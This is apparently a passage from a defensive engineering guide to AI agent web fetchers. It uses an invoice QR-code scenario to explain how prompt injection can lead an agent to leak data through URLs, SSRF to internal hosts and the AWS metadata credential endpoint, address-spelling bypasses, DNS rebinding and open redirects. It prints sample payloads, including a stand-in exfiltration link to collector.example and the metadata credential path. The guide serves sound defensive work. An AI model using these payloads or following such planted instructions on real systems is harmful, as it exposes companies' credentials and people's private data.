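If an address isn't in the index, OpenAI's system can direct the agent to look for another source without interrupting the user. This may work for a news article that is too new to be indexed, since a different site may have covered the same event. It wouldn't help with an online invoice, which the supplier probably publishes at only one address.

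If the user wants that particular page, the harness can ask before opening it. OpenAI shows a warning titled "Check this link is safe", which says the link isn't verified and may share conversation data with a third party. The warning displays the address and lets the user copy or open it.

OpenAI gives no data on how well people respond to this warning. It objects to lists of trusted sites on the grounds that false alarms teach people to click through warnings. The same objection would apply to its own check if many ordinary links failed it.

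Even a careful user may not have enough information to decide. Compare these addresses:

```
https://s.example/k7Qm2
https://s.example/QW5uYSBCZXJn
```

The second contains the name "Anna Berg" in Base64, a common way to encode data as text, and hardly anyone would recognise the name in that form. A useful warning should therefore state where the address came from, which the harness can record but the user can't see. "This link was in a QR code on page 1 of the invoice" gives the employee something to check with the supplier. If the warning reads "The assistant wrote this link itself", the employee has a good reason to refuse.

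A warning also can't reveal a leak in which the data is encoded in the choice of which addresses to open. Each address in ZombieAgent would look harmless, and if the addresses were in the public index, the user wouldn't see a warning at all.

### Checking a link can expose it

A cautious employee might paste the QR link into a URL scanning service, which visits an address and reports whether it seems malicious. A developer could also have the harness submit every doubtful link automatically. Either approach can reveal the information the checks are meant to protect, because some services publish the addresses they scan.

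*LEAKYLINKS*, by Mustafa, Rautenstrauch and colleagues, uses a boarding pass to illustrate the problem. An airline emails a passenger a link that opens the pass without a login. The passenger's employer automatically sends every emailed link to a scanner, which adds the full address to its public feed. Anyone watching the feed can then open the boarding pass.

The researchers examined 20 scanning services and found six that published full addresses in feeds not dominated by malicious sites: Anyrun, Cloudflare Radar, Hybrid Analysis, Joe Sandbox, URLQuery and URLScan. Between 10 October and 1 November 2025, they collected 2,286,501 different addresses from these feeds. Most were bare home pages, which can't contain a secret code. They removed those and the addresses Google had flagged as malicious, then visited the remaining 332,647.

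Their software then looked for signs that a page was meant to be private. It searched each address for random-looking strings that might serve as a password. If it found none, it deleted cookies and other stored data and reloaded the page to see whether the content changed. A vision model running on the researchers' own machines checked screenshots of the pages likely to be private for sensitive personal information.

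The model flagged 4,417 pages across 1,843 domains as containing sensitive information. The researchers checked 300 of them by hand and confirmed 291, a precision of 97%. They also checked 2,250 pages that the model had judged harmless and found 12 it had missed. After correcting for both kinds of error, they estimate that the feeds contained about 5,475 sensitive pages. These are a very small share of the addresses in the feeds, but the data covers only three weeks, and each page may expose someone's private affairs.

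The largest group, 1,411 pages, concerned email preferences and subscriptions. Another 761 involved logins, verification or password resets, and 391 involved bills, payments and orders. One page showed a person's visa application, including their passport details, and still had working controls for editing it. The researchers didn't submit any changes.

They also planted decoy pages and sent the addresses to the scanners. Outsiders visited the pages, often from suspicious IP addresses and with behaviour typical of people or programs probing for weaknesses. This shows that people are watching the feeds, though it doesn't prove that the visitors meant harm.

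For the accounts agent, the obvious risk is exposing a genuine online invoice. If the supplier protects the invoice only with a long random code in the link, submitting that link to a public scanner could publish the company's purchases and bank details. Mustafa and colleagues note that some services offer private scans, but scans are public by default, so a customer may have to choose the private setting.

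Even a private scan can leak data if the model composed the address. A scanner normally has to visit the page, which sends any data in the address to the site. If the harness blocked `https://collector.example/view?note=anna-berg` and then submitted it for scanning, the scanner would send Anna Berg's name to the attacker.

The study also gives reason to doubt that a public address is safe to open. A leaked private link is public, and a crawler might record it if another web page copied it from a feed. OpenAI's check would then let an agent open the link automatically. The request wouldn't reveal anything new from the conversation, which is all the check is meant to ensure, but it might still unsubscribe someone or use up their password-reset link.

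A harness can check a link without visiting the page or disclosing the path and query by looking up only the host name, such as `collector.example`, in a database of known malicious sites. This lookup reveals little about where a shortened link leads, because the host name is only that of the link shortener, such as `s.example`. If an invoice has a QR code containing a shortened link, the employee handling it is better off phoning the supplier to ask what the code is for.

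## How does a fetcher keep an agent away from private network addresses?

A URL can pass every check on its text and still lead to a machine inside the company. The owner of `coffee.example` could publish a harmless page, wait for a crawler to record it, and then point the domain's DNS record at `10.0.0.12`, a private address. The URL hasn't changed, so it still passes a public-index check. An attacker who took over a permitted supplier's DNS records could get past an allowlist in the same way. The fetcher therefore also has to check the IP address just before it connects.

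### How a stranger's link becomes an inside request

Server-side request forgery can succeed because many servers don't require a login for services on localhost, the name a machine uses for itself (OWASP, 2024). Such a service may return private data or carry out a privileged action because the request seems to come from a trusted source (agwa.name, *Preventing Server Side Request Forgery in Golang*).

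Take the invoice whose QR code holds `http://10.0.0.12/reports`. The fraudster can't open this address at home, where `10.0.0.12` is a different machine or none at all. The accounts agent can open it for them:

1. The harness decodes the QR code, and the model passes the address to the fetcher.
2. The fetcher runs on the company's cloud machine, so it can connect to `10.0.0.12`. The reports server receives a request from a neighbouring machine and returns the page without asking for a password.
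3. The harness adds the reports to the model's context.
4. Planted text gets the model to send the reports out, for example in the query of another link.

An attacker needs all four steps to read the reports, but the second step is enough to change a setting on an old device. An attacker could also map the network with a series of links, since an open port, a closed port and a missing machine usually produce different errors or delays.

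The attacker has to guess internal addresses, but some are easy to guess. Home routers often use `192.168.1.1`, and every machine can reach itself at `127.0.0.1`.

SSRF was fairly uncommon in the data behind OWASP's *A10:2021* (2021), with an average incidence rate of 2.72%, but it ranked first in OWASP's survey of the security community. The rate may be higher for agents, since every web fetcher requests addresses supplied from outside.

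Pydantic AI, a Python library for building agents, shows how little an attacker may need. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2980* (2026), a copy of the project's own advisory, describes chat applications in which a user can attach a file by giving its web address. For some combinations of model provider and file type, the library downloaded the file to the application's server before passing it to the model. The function that did this, `download_item()`, never checked whether the address was public. An attacker could claim to attach a PNG image and supply this address:

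```
http://169.254.169.254/latest/meta-data/iam/security-credentials/
```

This attack doesn't require a prompt injection, because the library makes the request before the model has received anything, so a more resistant model would not have prevented it. The flaw exposed applications that accepted message histories from outside users, but not those that used only addresses chosen by the developer. The project published the advisory on 6 February 2026, according to GCVE's *GHSA-2JRP-274C-JHV3* (2026), and fixed the flaw in version 1.56.0. The new version accepts only `http` and `https`, looks up the host name before the request and refuses private addresses unless the developer opts in.

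### What the metadata service hands out

The address in that attack belongs to the metadata service of Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business. It is the same on every AWS virtual machine, so the attacker doesn't have to guess it. AWS's *Add defense in depth against open firewalls, reverse proxies, and SSRF vulnerabilities* explains that the service was built to supply the credentials that programs on a cloud machine need to use other cloud services. Before it existed, developers had to write those credentials into the software or distribute them by hand.

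A company can give a machine a role, which is a set of permissions such as "read the invoice archive". Any program on the machine can then ask the metadata service for temporary credentials for that role. Under the original version, IMDSv1, two plain GET requests are enough. The address above returns the role's name, and the same address with the name added returns something like this, in shortened form:

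```
{
  "AccessKeyId" : "ASIA...",
  "SecretAccessKey" : "...",
  "Token" : "...",
  "Expiration" : "2026-10-07T18:00:00Z"
}
```

Anyone who obtains these values can usually act with the machine's permissions from their own computer until the credentials expire. In 2019, an attacker used SSRF to get such credentials from a server at Capital One, a US bank, and used them to reach customers' data. The attacker stole more than 100 million credit applications, according to agwa.name.

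The service also returns "user data", up to 16 KB of text that the company supplies for the machine, often a setup script. AWS's *Access instance metadata for an EC2 instance* shows that a program can retrieve it with one request. If the company has left a database password in the script, the fetcher can read the password.

AWS announced a second version, IMDSv2, in 2019. A program must now start by asking for a token with a PUT request, a method that ordinary links never use, and then include the token in every later request:

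```
PUT /latest/api/token
X-aws-ec2-metadata-token-ttl-seconds: 21600

GET /latest/meta-data/iam/security-credentials/
X-aws-ec2-metadata-token: <token from the first reply>
```

The number in the PUT request is the token's lifetime in seconds, here the maximum of six hours. A GET request without a valid token gets a "401 Unauthorized" error, according to AWS's *How Instance Metadata Service Version 2 works*. A fetcher that can only send GET requests and doesn't let the model choose the headers can't obtain a token or use one. AWS says its analysis of real vulnerabilities found this design effective against the vast majority of SSRF flaws, but it gives no figures.

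IMDSv2 also limits how far the token can travel. Each device that forwards a packet lowers a counter in it by one and discards the packet when the counter reaches zero. By default, the counter starts at one for the packet carrying the token, so the packet can't leave the machine. A program in a container can fail to get a token, because forwarding the packet into the container also lowers the counter. AWS suggests raising the starting value to two when software in containers needs the metadata service. But if the fetcher runs in a container and needs no cloud credentials, leaving the value at one protects it.

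IMDSv2 helps only if the company turns IMDSv1 off. AWS kept IMDSv1 running for customers whose tools depended on it, and by default a machine can still use both, so an attacker would use the version that needs no token. Some machine images come with a stricter setting. Machines started from Amazon Linux 2023 accept only IMDSv2, though with a hop limit of two, according to AWS's *IMDSv2*.

An agent that can run code can send the PUT request, read the token and attach it, as any legitimate program would. For such an agent, the company should disable the metadata service, which AWS allows, or give the machine a role with hardly any permissions. IMDSv2 also doesn't protect the reports server at `10.0.0.12`, so the fetcher still needs to refuse private addresses.

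### Which addresses to refuse

The Internet Assigned Numbers Authority (IANA), which coordinates the internet's numbering, keeps registries of address ranges with special uses. The table below draws on two of these registries, *IPv4 Special-Purpose Address Space* (2009) and *IPv6 Special-Purpose Address Space* (2006), both last updated in October 2025.

An IPv4 address has 32 bits, written as four numbers from 0 to 255. An IPv6 address has 128 bits, written in hexadecimal, and a double colon stands for a run of zeros. In a range such as `10.0.0.0/8`, the number after the slash is how many bits at the start are fixed, so this range covers every address whose first number is 10. The range `172.16.0.0/12` runs from `172.16.0.0` to `172.31.255.255`.

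| Range | Purpose | What a fetcher might reach there |
|---|---|---|
| `0.0.0.0/8` | "This network" | `0.0.0.0` leads to the local machine on many systems |
| `10.0.0.0/8`, `172.16.0.0/12` | Private use | Office and cloud networks |
| `192.168.0.0/16` | Private use | Home routers and small office networks |
| `100.64.0.0/10` | Shared address space, mainly for internet providers | Provider equipment and Alibaba Cloud's metadata service at `100.100.100.200` |
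| `127.0.0.0/8` | Loopback | Programs on the fetcher's own machine |
| `169.254.0.0/16` | Link-local, for directly connected devices | Cloud metadata services |
| `192.0.0.0/24` | Protocol assignments | Special network functions |
| `192.0.2.0/24`, `198.51.100.0/24`, `203.0.113.0/24` | Examples in documentation | Nothing legitimate |
| `198.18.0.0/15` | Benchmarking network equipment | Test networks |
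| `240.0.0.0/4` | Reserved, including the broadcast address | Nothing legitimate |
| `::/128` | Unspecified address | The local machine on some systems |
| `::1/128` | Loopback | Programs on the fetcher's own machine |
| `::ffff:0:0/96` | IPv4 addresses written as IPv6 | Any IPv4 address, including private ones |
| `64:ff9b::/96`, `64:ff9b:1::/48` | Translation between IPv6 and IPv4 | Any IPv4 address that the network will translate |
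| `100::/64` | Discarding unwanted traffic | Nothing legitimate |
| `2001::/23` | Protocol assignments, including the Teredo tunnel | Special network functions, and IPv4 addresses through Teredo |
| `2002::/16` | 6to4, another way to carry IPv6 over IPv4 | An IPv4 address inside the IPv6 one |
| `2001:db8::/32`, `3fff::/20` | Examples in documentation | Nothing legitimate |
| `5f00::/16` | Segment routing inside a provider's network | Network equipment |
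| `fc00::/7` | Unique local addresses, the IPv6 form of private use | Internal machines and AWS's IPv6 metadata address, `fd00:ec2::254` |
| `fe80::/10` | Link-local | Devices on the same local network |

The fetcher should also refuse multicast addresses, which deliver one message to a group of machines. These are in `224.0.0.0/4` and `ff00::/8`, which IANA lists separately. An old range for internal IPv6 networks, `fec0::/10`, is also worth blocking because some software no longer treats it as private.

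Each entry in IANA's registries has a column that shows whether the range is "globally reachable". A developer might be tempted to refuse every range marked "false" and accept the rest. This would handle most of the table correctly, but IANA marks `64:ff9b::/96` as globally reachable and gives no yes or no for Teredo and 6to4. All of these can carry an IPv4 address inside them. In hexadecimal, 169 is `a9` and 254 is `fe`, so this IPv6 address contains the address of the metadata service:

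```
64:ff9b::a9fe:a9fe
```

On a network that translates such addresses, the request could arrive at `169.254.169.254`.

This gap affected Pydantic AI's repaired version. Its `allow-local` option let applications fetch internal files, but the developers promised that cloud metadata addresses would stay blocked. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2978* (2026) describes how an attacker could bypass that block by putting the metadata address inside an IPv6 address. Version 1.99.0 extracted the IPv4 address from three such formats and checked it. In June, GitLab's *CVE-2026-48782* (2026) reported that the fix had missed several other formats, including `64:ff9b:1::/48` and prefixes that a network operator can choose freely. Exploiting either flaw required `allow-local`, an address that an outsider could influence and a network that would deliver the request, so far fewer applications were at risk than from the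 original flaw.

For IPv6, a developer can avoid much of this work by starting from the addresses to allow rather than the ones to block. IANA currently allocates ordinary public IPv6 addresses only from `2000::/3`, the addresses whose first digit is 2 or 3. The fetcher can refuse everything outside that range, along with the special ranges inside it. It would still miss a translation prefix that the network's operator chose from the public range, so someone has to ask the operator whether there is one.

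On some IPv6-only networks, every website that has only an IPv4 address appears under `64:ff9b::/96`, so refusing the whole range would cut off much of the web. On these networks, the fetcher should extract the last 32 bits of the address and test them as an IPv4 address.

Standard libraries include checks for most of these ranges, but their definitions of "private" vary. Pydantic AI's original advisory gave users who couldn't upgrade a temporary filter based on Python's `is_private` test and two similar ones. Python doesn't count `100.64.0.0/10` as private, so the filter would have allowed `100.100.100.200`, one of the metadata addresses listed in the advisory. Python's `is_global` test handles that range correctly and is a better starting point, although it accepts `64:ff9b::/96`.

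Some universities and large companies use public IPv4 addresses internally, and IPv6 often gives office computers public addresses, with a firewall to keep strangers out. Public registries can't list these machines as internal, so if the fetcher runs behind the firewall, the organization needs to add its own ranges to the table.

### One address, many spellings

A developer might try to protect the agent's own machine by refusing any URL that contains `127.0.0.1` or `localhost`. But many programs accept other ways of writing the same address:

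| Host in the URL | Why it leads to 127.0.0.1 |
|---|---|
| `2130706433` | The 32 bits as a single number, 127 × 256³ + 1 |
| `0x7f000001` | The same number in hexadecimal, where `7f` is 127 |
| `0177.0.0.1` | The leading zero marks an octal number, and 177 in octal is 127 |
| `127.1` | The missing parts count as zeros |
| `[::ffff:127.0.0.1]` | The IPv4 address written as an IPv6 one |
| `127.0.0.1.nip.io` | A public DNS service returns the address in the name |

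All of `127.0.0.0/8` is loopback, so `127.0.0.2` and about 16 million other addresses usually also lead to the same machine. Text matching can block public websites too. For example, a rule against hosts that begin with `10.` would block `10.example.com`.

The last row of the table is the most important, because the owner of any domain can set its DNS record to `127.0.0.1` or `169.254.169.254`. The URL then doesn't show the address it leads to.

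PraisonAI, a framework for building teams of agents, had a check that recognised numeric spellings of private addresses but never looked up host names. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3535* (2026) reproduces the project's advisory for this flaw. An earlier repair had added the decimal, hexadecimal and shortened forms. Kai Aizen, the security researcher who reported the new flaw, found that the check refused `2130706433` and `0x7f000001` but accepted `metadata-thief.com`, whatever its DNS record contained. The function was documented as catching host names that resolve to internal machines.

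Aizen showed that the check never looked up the name by replacing Python's lookup function with one that raised an error whenever a program called it. The check ran without an error. The code returned "not blocked" for any text that was neither a recognisable IP address nor on a short list of forbidden names. An attacker could reach the flaw through the framework's web-scraping tools, or through a feature that fetches any address a user mentions in a prompt. In both cases the fetched content went into the model's context.

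Another file in the same package already looked up hostnames and checked every resulting address. CERT.hr's *CVE-2026-55526*, a record of a closely related report, describes a fix that does the same for the scraping tools and refuses the request if the lookup fails. It lists 1.6.58 as the fixed version, but OSV and GitLab's *GHSA-vxgj-xg5c-p4h7* (2026) list 1.6.59, so users should install 1.6.59 or later.

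### Look up once, test, then connect

The fetcher can handle every spelling in the same way if it converts the host to IP addresses before testing anything. In pseudocode, the procedure is:

```
function fetch(url):
    parts = parse(url)
    if parts.scheme is not "https": refuse

    addresses = look_up(parts.host)        # all IPv4 and IPv6 results
    if the lookup failed or found nothing: refuse

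    for each address in addresses:
        if address is in a refused range: refuse

    connection = connect(addresses[0], parts.port)    # no second lookup
    start encryption, checking the certificate for parts.host
    send the request, with parts.host in the Host header
```

On most systems, the lookup function also converts numeric spellings of an address, so the developer doesn't have to think of every format. For example, it turns `2130706433` into `127.0.0.1`, which the loop then rejects like any other loopback address.

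The loop tests every result because a name can have several addresses. If an attacker's domain returned one public and one private address, a fetcher that tested only the public one might later try the private one, for instance if the first connection failed. Pydantic AI's temporary filter has a further weakness because Python's older `gethostbyname` function returns only one IPv4 address and ignores IPv6. The newer `getaddrinfo` returns both IPv4 and IPv6 addresses.

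A fetcher has to refuse a URL if the DNS lookup for its domain fails. SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55537* reports that PraisonAI's check on webhooks (URLs to which a program sends a message when a job finishes) accepted the URL when the lookup failed. The program then looked up the domain again when it sent the message, minutes or hours later. An attacker who ran the domain's DNS server could leave the first lookup unanswered and answer the second with an internal address.

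The certificate check needs the original host name because website certificates normally name a domain. If the fetcher checked the certificate against the numeric address instead, the check would fail for nearly every site, and a developer might turn it off. The description of a fetching library on PyPI, the public index of Python packages, warns that turning it off would create a worse vulnerability than SSRF, since anyone able to intercept the connection could impersonate the site. The fetcher should use the numeric address only to open the connection, and use the name for the certificate check and the Host header, which a server with many websites needs to return the right one.

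FastMCP, a framework for building tools that models can call, documents a function called `ssrf_safe_fetch` that follows much the same steps. It accepts only HTTPS URLs, checks the addresses that the hostname resolves to, and connects to an address it has checked.

Requiring HTTPS gives some protection even if the address test has a bug. AWS's metadata service and many internal administration pages use plain HTTP, so an encrypted connection to them fails. An internal server that does use HTTPS won't have a certificate for the attacker's domain. However, the connection attempt can still reveal whether a port is open, and requiring HTTPS also blocks some public sites that only use plain HTTP.

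The fetcher should run its allowlist, provenance or index check before the DNS lookup, because the lookup sends data out. If the model asks for `anna-berg.collector.example`, the query goes to a DNS server that the attacker may run, which leaks Anna Berg's name even if the fetcher then refuses the connection. The fetcher also has to repeat the whole procedure after a redirect. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-55524* (2026) reports that PraisonAI's `web_crawl` tool failed to do this.

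### DNS rebinding

The comment "no second lookup" in the pseudocode is there to prevent DNS rebinding, in which an attacker changes the address behind a name between the check and the connection. The attacker runs the DNS server for a domain and can therefore give a different answer each time. With invented times, an attack on a fetcher that looks up the name twice would go like this:

| Time | What happens | Answer from the attacker's DNS server |
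|---|---|---|
| 0.00 s | The check looks up `rebind.example` | `1.1.1.1`, to be stored for 0 seconds |
| 0.05 s | The check finds a public address and approves the URL | |
| 0.20 s | The fetcher looks up `rebind.example` to connect | `127.0.0.1` |
| 0.21 s | The fetcher connects to its own machine | |

DNS answers normally include a time for which a computer may store and reuse them. The attacker sets this time to zero, which makes a second lookup more likely. Both lookups work properly and the check tests the first answer correctly, but it is a mistake to assume that the second answer will be the same.

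WeKnora, Tencent's open-source system for searching and questioning documents, had this flaw in its `web_fetch` tool. GCVE's *GHSA-H6GW-8F77-MMMP* (2026), a copy of the project's advisory for CVE-2026-30858, explains that the tool checked each URL and then passed it to a headless browser (a browser that runs without a window and is controlled by software). The browser received the host name rather than the checked address, so it did its own lookup.

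The demonstration used a DNS server that returned `1.1.1.1` to the first query and a local address to later ones. When the agent was asked to fetch a page from the domain, the tool returned content from a web server on its own machine. The advisory's text gives the local address as `127.0.0.1`, but the DNS server's configuration contains `0.0.0.0`, which is a good reason to include `0.0.0.0/8` in the list of refused ranges. The attack could take several attempts, but that is a small inconvenience for an attacker who can keep asking the agent to open the page.

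The fetcher has to connect to the exact address it tested, a technique called pinning. Shortening the gap between the lookups doesn't solve the problem, because the attacker's server can return a different address for each query. The library on PyPI enforces pinning by passing only an IP address to the function that opens the connection, so the function has no name to look up. The library's developer tested it with a real DNS server that changed its record during a request.

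Pinning is harder with a browser. A developer can tell some browsers which IP address to use for a given name, but one page may load images and scripts from dozens of other names, each of which needs its own check. It is usually simpler to send all of the browser's traffic through a proxy that looks up each name, checks the results and makes the connection itself. WeKnora's advisory lists version 0.3.0 as fixed but doesn't describe the change, so a company that relies on the tool should test it with its own rebinding server.

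It is similarly unclear whether PraisonAI's fix pins the address. Aizen recommended pinning as well as looking up names, but CERT.hr's summary of the fix mentions only the lookup. If the fetcher still does a second lookup when it connects, a fixed DNS record would no longer work for an attacker, but rebinding still could.

Pinning doesn't help when the tested address is public but gives access to something private. For example, a supplier's website might show extra pages to any visitor from the company's IP address, and the fetcher would reach them through an ordinary public connection. A website that needs to protect such pages should require a login.

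### When the agent needs an internal page

Some agents have good reasons to use internal services. The company might want the accounts agent to check each invoice against a purchase order on the server at `10.0.0.12`. A developer could make an exception for that address in the fetcher, but the fetcher would then also allow any link in an invoice that points to that server.

A developer sets Pydantic AI's `allow-local` option for a particular file address, but the option permits private addresses in general, except for the metadata services. An outsider who can influence that file address can point it at any internal machine the application can reach. The project's later flaws affected only applications that had used this option.

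It is safer to leave the web fetcher's rule without exceptions and build a separate tool for the internal service. The tool doesn't need to accept a URL at all:

```
Tool:      get_purchase_order
Input:     order number, exactly 8 digits
Request:   GET https://orders.corp.example/orders/{order number}
Connects:  only to 10.0.0.12, port 443
Redirects: refused
```

The model supplies only the order number, and the harness builds the address. Malicious instructions in an invoice might get the model to look up the wrong order, but they can't make the tool contact the metadata service or an administration page. If the agent later needs a second internal service, the developer can add it to a short list of exact hosts and ports.

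The tool should log in with its own account, which can read purchase orders and do nothing else. The orders server can then refuse requests from inside the network that lack a login, including any that a bug in the web fetcher lets through.

Coding agents on laptops often need a similar exception, because programmers test websites on their own machines. A programmer working on a site at `http://localhost:3000` can permit that host and port for the project. Permitting all of `localhost` would also expose the test database, and perhaps a password manager or another agent that accepts commands on a different port.

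Data that an agent reads through a separate tool can still leak. Once a purchase order is in the model's context, planted text may lead the model to send it out through the web fetcher, just as it could with an email. The accounts agent can avoid this if its web allowlist stays empty. If the company permits a few supplier portals, the harness could turn off web access for the rest of a task once the agent has read a purchase order. The agent would then have to download any invoice copies before reading the order.

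## What limits should apply to redirects and to the content that comes back?

Even after a fetcher approves a public address and connects to the exact machine it tested, the server can redirect it to a private address such as `10.0.0.12`. A stranger also chooses the format, size and text of any page the fetcher receives.

### How a redirect works

A redirect is a reply whose status code begins with 3, usually with a `Location` header that holds the new address. The invoice's short link might return this:

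```
HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: https://supplier.example/invoice/8841
```

Codes 301 and 308 mean that a page has moved permanently, while 302 and 307 mean it has moved temporarily. Code 303 points to a different page that answers the request indirectly. After a 307 or 308, a client that follows the redirect automatically must keep the original request method, so a tool that submits forms could send the form's contents to a new host.

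The IETF's HTTP standard allows clients to follow redirects automatically but doesn't require it. Many HTTP libraries do so by default, including the Python library curl_cffi. Its *Security* documentation describes this default as fine for desktop programs but dangerous on servers that fetch addresses supplied by users.

The operator of a link shortener, or the person who created a short link, may be able to change its destination later, so an employee who tested the link in the morning can't be sure where it leads in the afternoon.

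An open redirect is a page on an otherwise trustworthy site that sends visitors to any address in its own parameters. Montana State University's *Unvalidated Redirects and Forwards* gives the example of a page called `redirect.php` with a parameter named `url`. If a supplier had such a page, an attacker could write:

```
https://supplier.example/go?url=https://collector.example/view
```

The link begins with the supplier's real name, which OWASP's *16.1 Safe from unsafe redirects* notes makes phishing more convincing. It also passes an allowlist that includes `supplier.example`. If the fetcher then follows the redirect without another check, a single page with an unsafe redirect on a permitted site lets the agent reach the whole web. The model could also add Anna Berg's name to the address inside the link, and the redirect would send it to the attacker.

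### Checking every hop

Datadog's *Route follows redirections from external APIs*, a rule in a security monitoring product, advises developers to switch off automatic following or, if they need redirects, to validate the target. A fetcher should do both. It switches off the library's own following and handles each redirect in a loop:

```
function fetch_page(url):
    repeat at most 6 times:              # the first request and 5 redirects
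        if url.scheme is not "https": refuse
        if url fails the allowlist or index check: stop and report url
        look up the host, test every IP address, connect to a tested one
        reply = request(url, new headers, follow_redirects = false)
        if reply is not a redirect: return reply
        url = resolve(reply.Location, relative to url)
    refuse
```

A redirect's target may be relative, such as `/invoice/8841`, so the fetcher has to combine it with the current address before testing the result. The fetcher can't assume that every target beginning with a slash is on the same site, because `//collector.example/8841` names a different host.

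The checks also apply to redirects that stay on the same host. The host's DNS record may have changed since the last request, and an allowlist that permits only `example.com/blog` shouldn't allow a redirect to another part of `example.com`.

The IETF recommends that clients detect redirect loops. A hostile server can invent a new address for each redirect, so remembering past addresses isn't enough and the fetcher needs a fixed cap. A cap of five redirects leaves room for a link shortener and a site that has moved. The harness can prompt the user if a longer chain is needed.

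Each request needs new headers because the old ones may contain credentials. If the harness adds an API key to its requests for the supplier's portal, and the portal redirects to `collector.example`, a fetcher that copies the headers will send the key to the attacker. The IETF's standard recommends removing `Authorization` and `Cookie` headers that the client generated itself, but it only recommends considering removal for headers that the calling program added, so a developer who adds a key by hand shouldn't assume the library will drop it. The `Referer` header needs the same treatment, since it can reveal the previous address and any secret code in it.

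Following a redirect from `https` to `http` removes the encryption, so anyone on the route can read the request or alter the reply. It also undoes the protection that requiring HTTPS gives internal services. The loop refuses such redirects, though the fetcher could first try the same address with `https`. Anthropic's Claude Code upgrades plain HTTP addresses this way.

### PraisonAI checked only the first address

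The `web_crawl` tool in PraisonAI, the agent framework whose earlier check never looked up host names, needed two fixes. GitLab's *CVE-2026-40160* (2026) describes the first flaw, published in April. On a new installation, the tool requested any address it received without checking the host, and it followed redirects.

The first repair checked the original URL but not the redirects. The tool looked up the host name, refused private addresses and then passed the URL to a library that followed redirects automatically. An attacker could supply a link to their own public server, which would pass the check, and have that server redirect the tool to the metadata service. The security company Rapid7, which reproduces the record for this flaw (CVE-2026-55524), notes that the tool returned the body of the final reply. On a cloud machine that still used the older metadata service, that reply could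 contain the machine's credentials.

In its entry for a related record, CVE-2026-55523, Rapid7 describes the redirect problem as an incomplete fix of the earlier flaws. In June, GitLab's *GHSA-6h9p-93hq-q7h6* (2026) reported the same mistake in SpiderTools, PraisonAI's web-scraping tools, which rejected private addresses in the original URL but never checked the `Location` header.

According to SecureLayer7, PraisonAI version 1.6.58 turns off automatic redirect following in `web_crawl`, checks the target of every redirect and connects to the IP address it has checked. Another file in the package had already turned off automatic redirects. PraisonAI had several fetchers, each with its own version of the check, so an attacker could use whichever had the weakest one. If a framework's tools all shared one fetch function, a developer could make this kind of fix once.

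### Following silently or stopping to report

A fetcher that checks every hop could still follow the whole redirect chain without reporting it. Claude Code's fetcher does this only for some redirects. *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools* found in 2025 that it followed redirects within one host. Anthropic's documentation confirms that when a redirect leads to a different host, the fetcher stops and returns a short text with the original address and the target. Claude needs a second tool call to open the target.

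The harness can apply its usual permission rules to that second call, so manual mode's prompt for unlisted sites also covers the redirect's target. The `auto` and `bypassPermissions` modes skip this prompt unless a rule specifically requires it, but the call still goes through Anthropic's domain safety check by default.

Stopping at a redirect and reporting the new address to the model protects the user only if something other than the model checks the second call, because a model that followed a planted instruction to open the first address will probably open the next one too. The harness should record the new address as coming from a redirect, even if the user typed the original link, because the address is text from an untrusted server.

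The report shows the employee the name of the destination behind the short link. The fetcher can get that name from the shortener without visiting the destination. Reporting redirects adds an extra step for many innocent ones, such as one from `supplier.example` to `www.supplier.example`. The developer can avoid most of these extra steps by adding both names to the list.

### The invoice's link, hop by hop

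Suppose the accounts agent has reported the QR code, and the employee asks it to open that one link. The company's allowlist already includes `supplier.example`, whose website has an open redirect. A fraudster has prepared this chain:

| Step | Address requested | Reply | Check on the next address |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `https://s.example/k7Qm2` | Redirect to `https://supplier.example/go?url=https://view.example/8841` | Passes, because the host is on the list |
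| 2 | `https://supplier.example/go?url=https://view.example/8841` | Redirect to `https://view.example/8841` | Fails, because the host is unknown |
| 3 | `https://view.example/8841` | Redirect to `http://10.0.0.12/reports` | Fails, because it uses plain HTTP and a private address |
| 4 | `http://10.0.0.12/reports` | The company's internal reports | |

A fetcher that checks only the short link completes all four steps and adds the reports to the model's context. The loop stops after step 2 and reports `view.example`. Even if the employee approved that address too, the loop would refuse to go from step 3 to step 4.

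The employee should still phone before opening `view.example`, because the supplier's name in the middle of the logged chain shows only that the supplier's website forwards visitors.

### Redirects inside the page

A page can also redirect visitors through its own code. W3C's *Techniques for WCAG 2.0* describes the meta refresh, an HTML element that makes the browser request another address after a set delay, or immediately if the delay is zero. A script can do the same by changing the page's location.

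A plain fetcher handles a page that redirects through its own code like any other successful reply. It downloads the code but doesn't act on it, so the redirect never happens. If the model finds the new address in the text and tries to open it, the harness can check the new tool call.

A browser acts on both kinds of code, so a check limited to 3xx replies would miss them. The harness has to examine every address the browser tries to open, for example at the proxy that handles its DNS lookups.

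The employee's browser may also end up somewhere other than the destination in the fetcher's report. If the report lists `view.example`, the HTTP redirects end there, but a script on the page might send the browser elsewhere. The server can also send agents to one page and people to another. Claude Code's requests, for instance, can be recognized by a `User-Agent` header beginning with `Claude-User`.

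### Limits on the reply

Once the redirects end, the fetcher has to decide how much of the reply to accept and what to do with it.

| Control | Harm it stops | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Accept only permitted file types | Programs and archives reach software that might run or unpack them | A permitted file may exploit a bug in the software that reads it |
| Limit the download | A huge file fills the disk or ties up the connection | A small file may expand when unpacked |
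| Limit the unpacked size | The expanded file uses up the memory | |
| Limit the text given to the model | A long page raises the bill and crowds out the task | A short page can still contain an instruction |
| Set one deadline for the whole fetch | A slow server keeps the agent waiting | |
| Run no scripts | Page code redirects the browser or sends requests of its own | Some sites appear empty |
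| Send and store no cookies | The request uses someone's login, or the site links several visits | The IP address may still identify the company |
| Extract the text | Pictures and page code reach the model | Text hidden from people may survive |

A server states the file type in the `Content-Type` header, but it can put anything there, so the fetcher should compare the stated type with the file's first bytes. A PDF normally begins with `%PDF-`, a PNG image with a fixed eight-byte signature, and a modern Word file with `PK`, because it is a zip archive. Plain text has no signature, so the fetcher has to check that the bytes decode as text.

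Anthropic's fetcher for developers accepts only text and PDFs, and returns an error for other types. To prevent SSRF, Red Hat similarly advises confirming that a reply is what the application expected before passing it on. Such a check could have limited the damage in the Pydantic AI attack, where an attacker could attach the metadata service's address as a PNG image. The service returns text, so checking for the PNG signature would have kept the credentials away from the model. It wouldn't have prevented the request, and it wouldn't help a fetcher that expects text.

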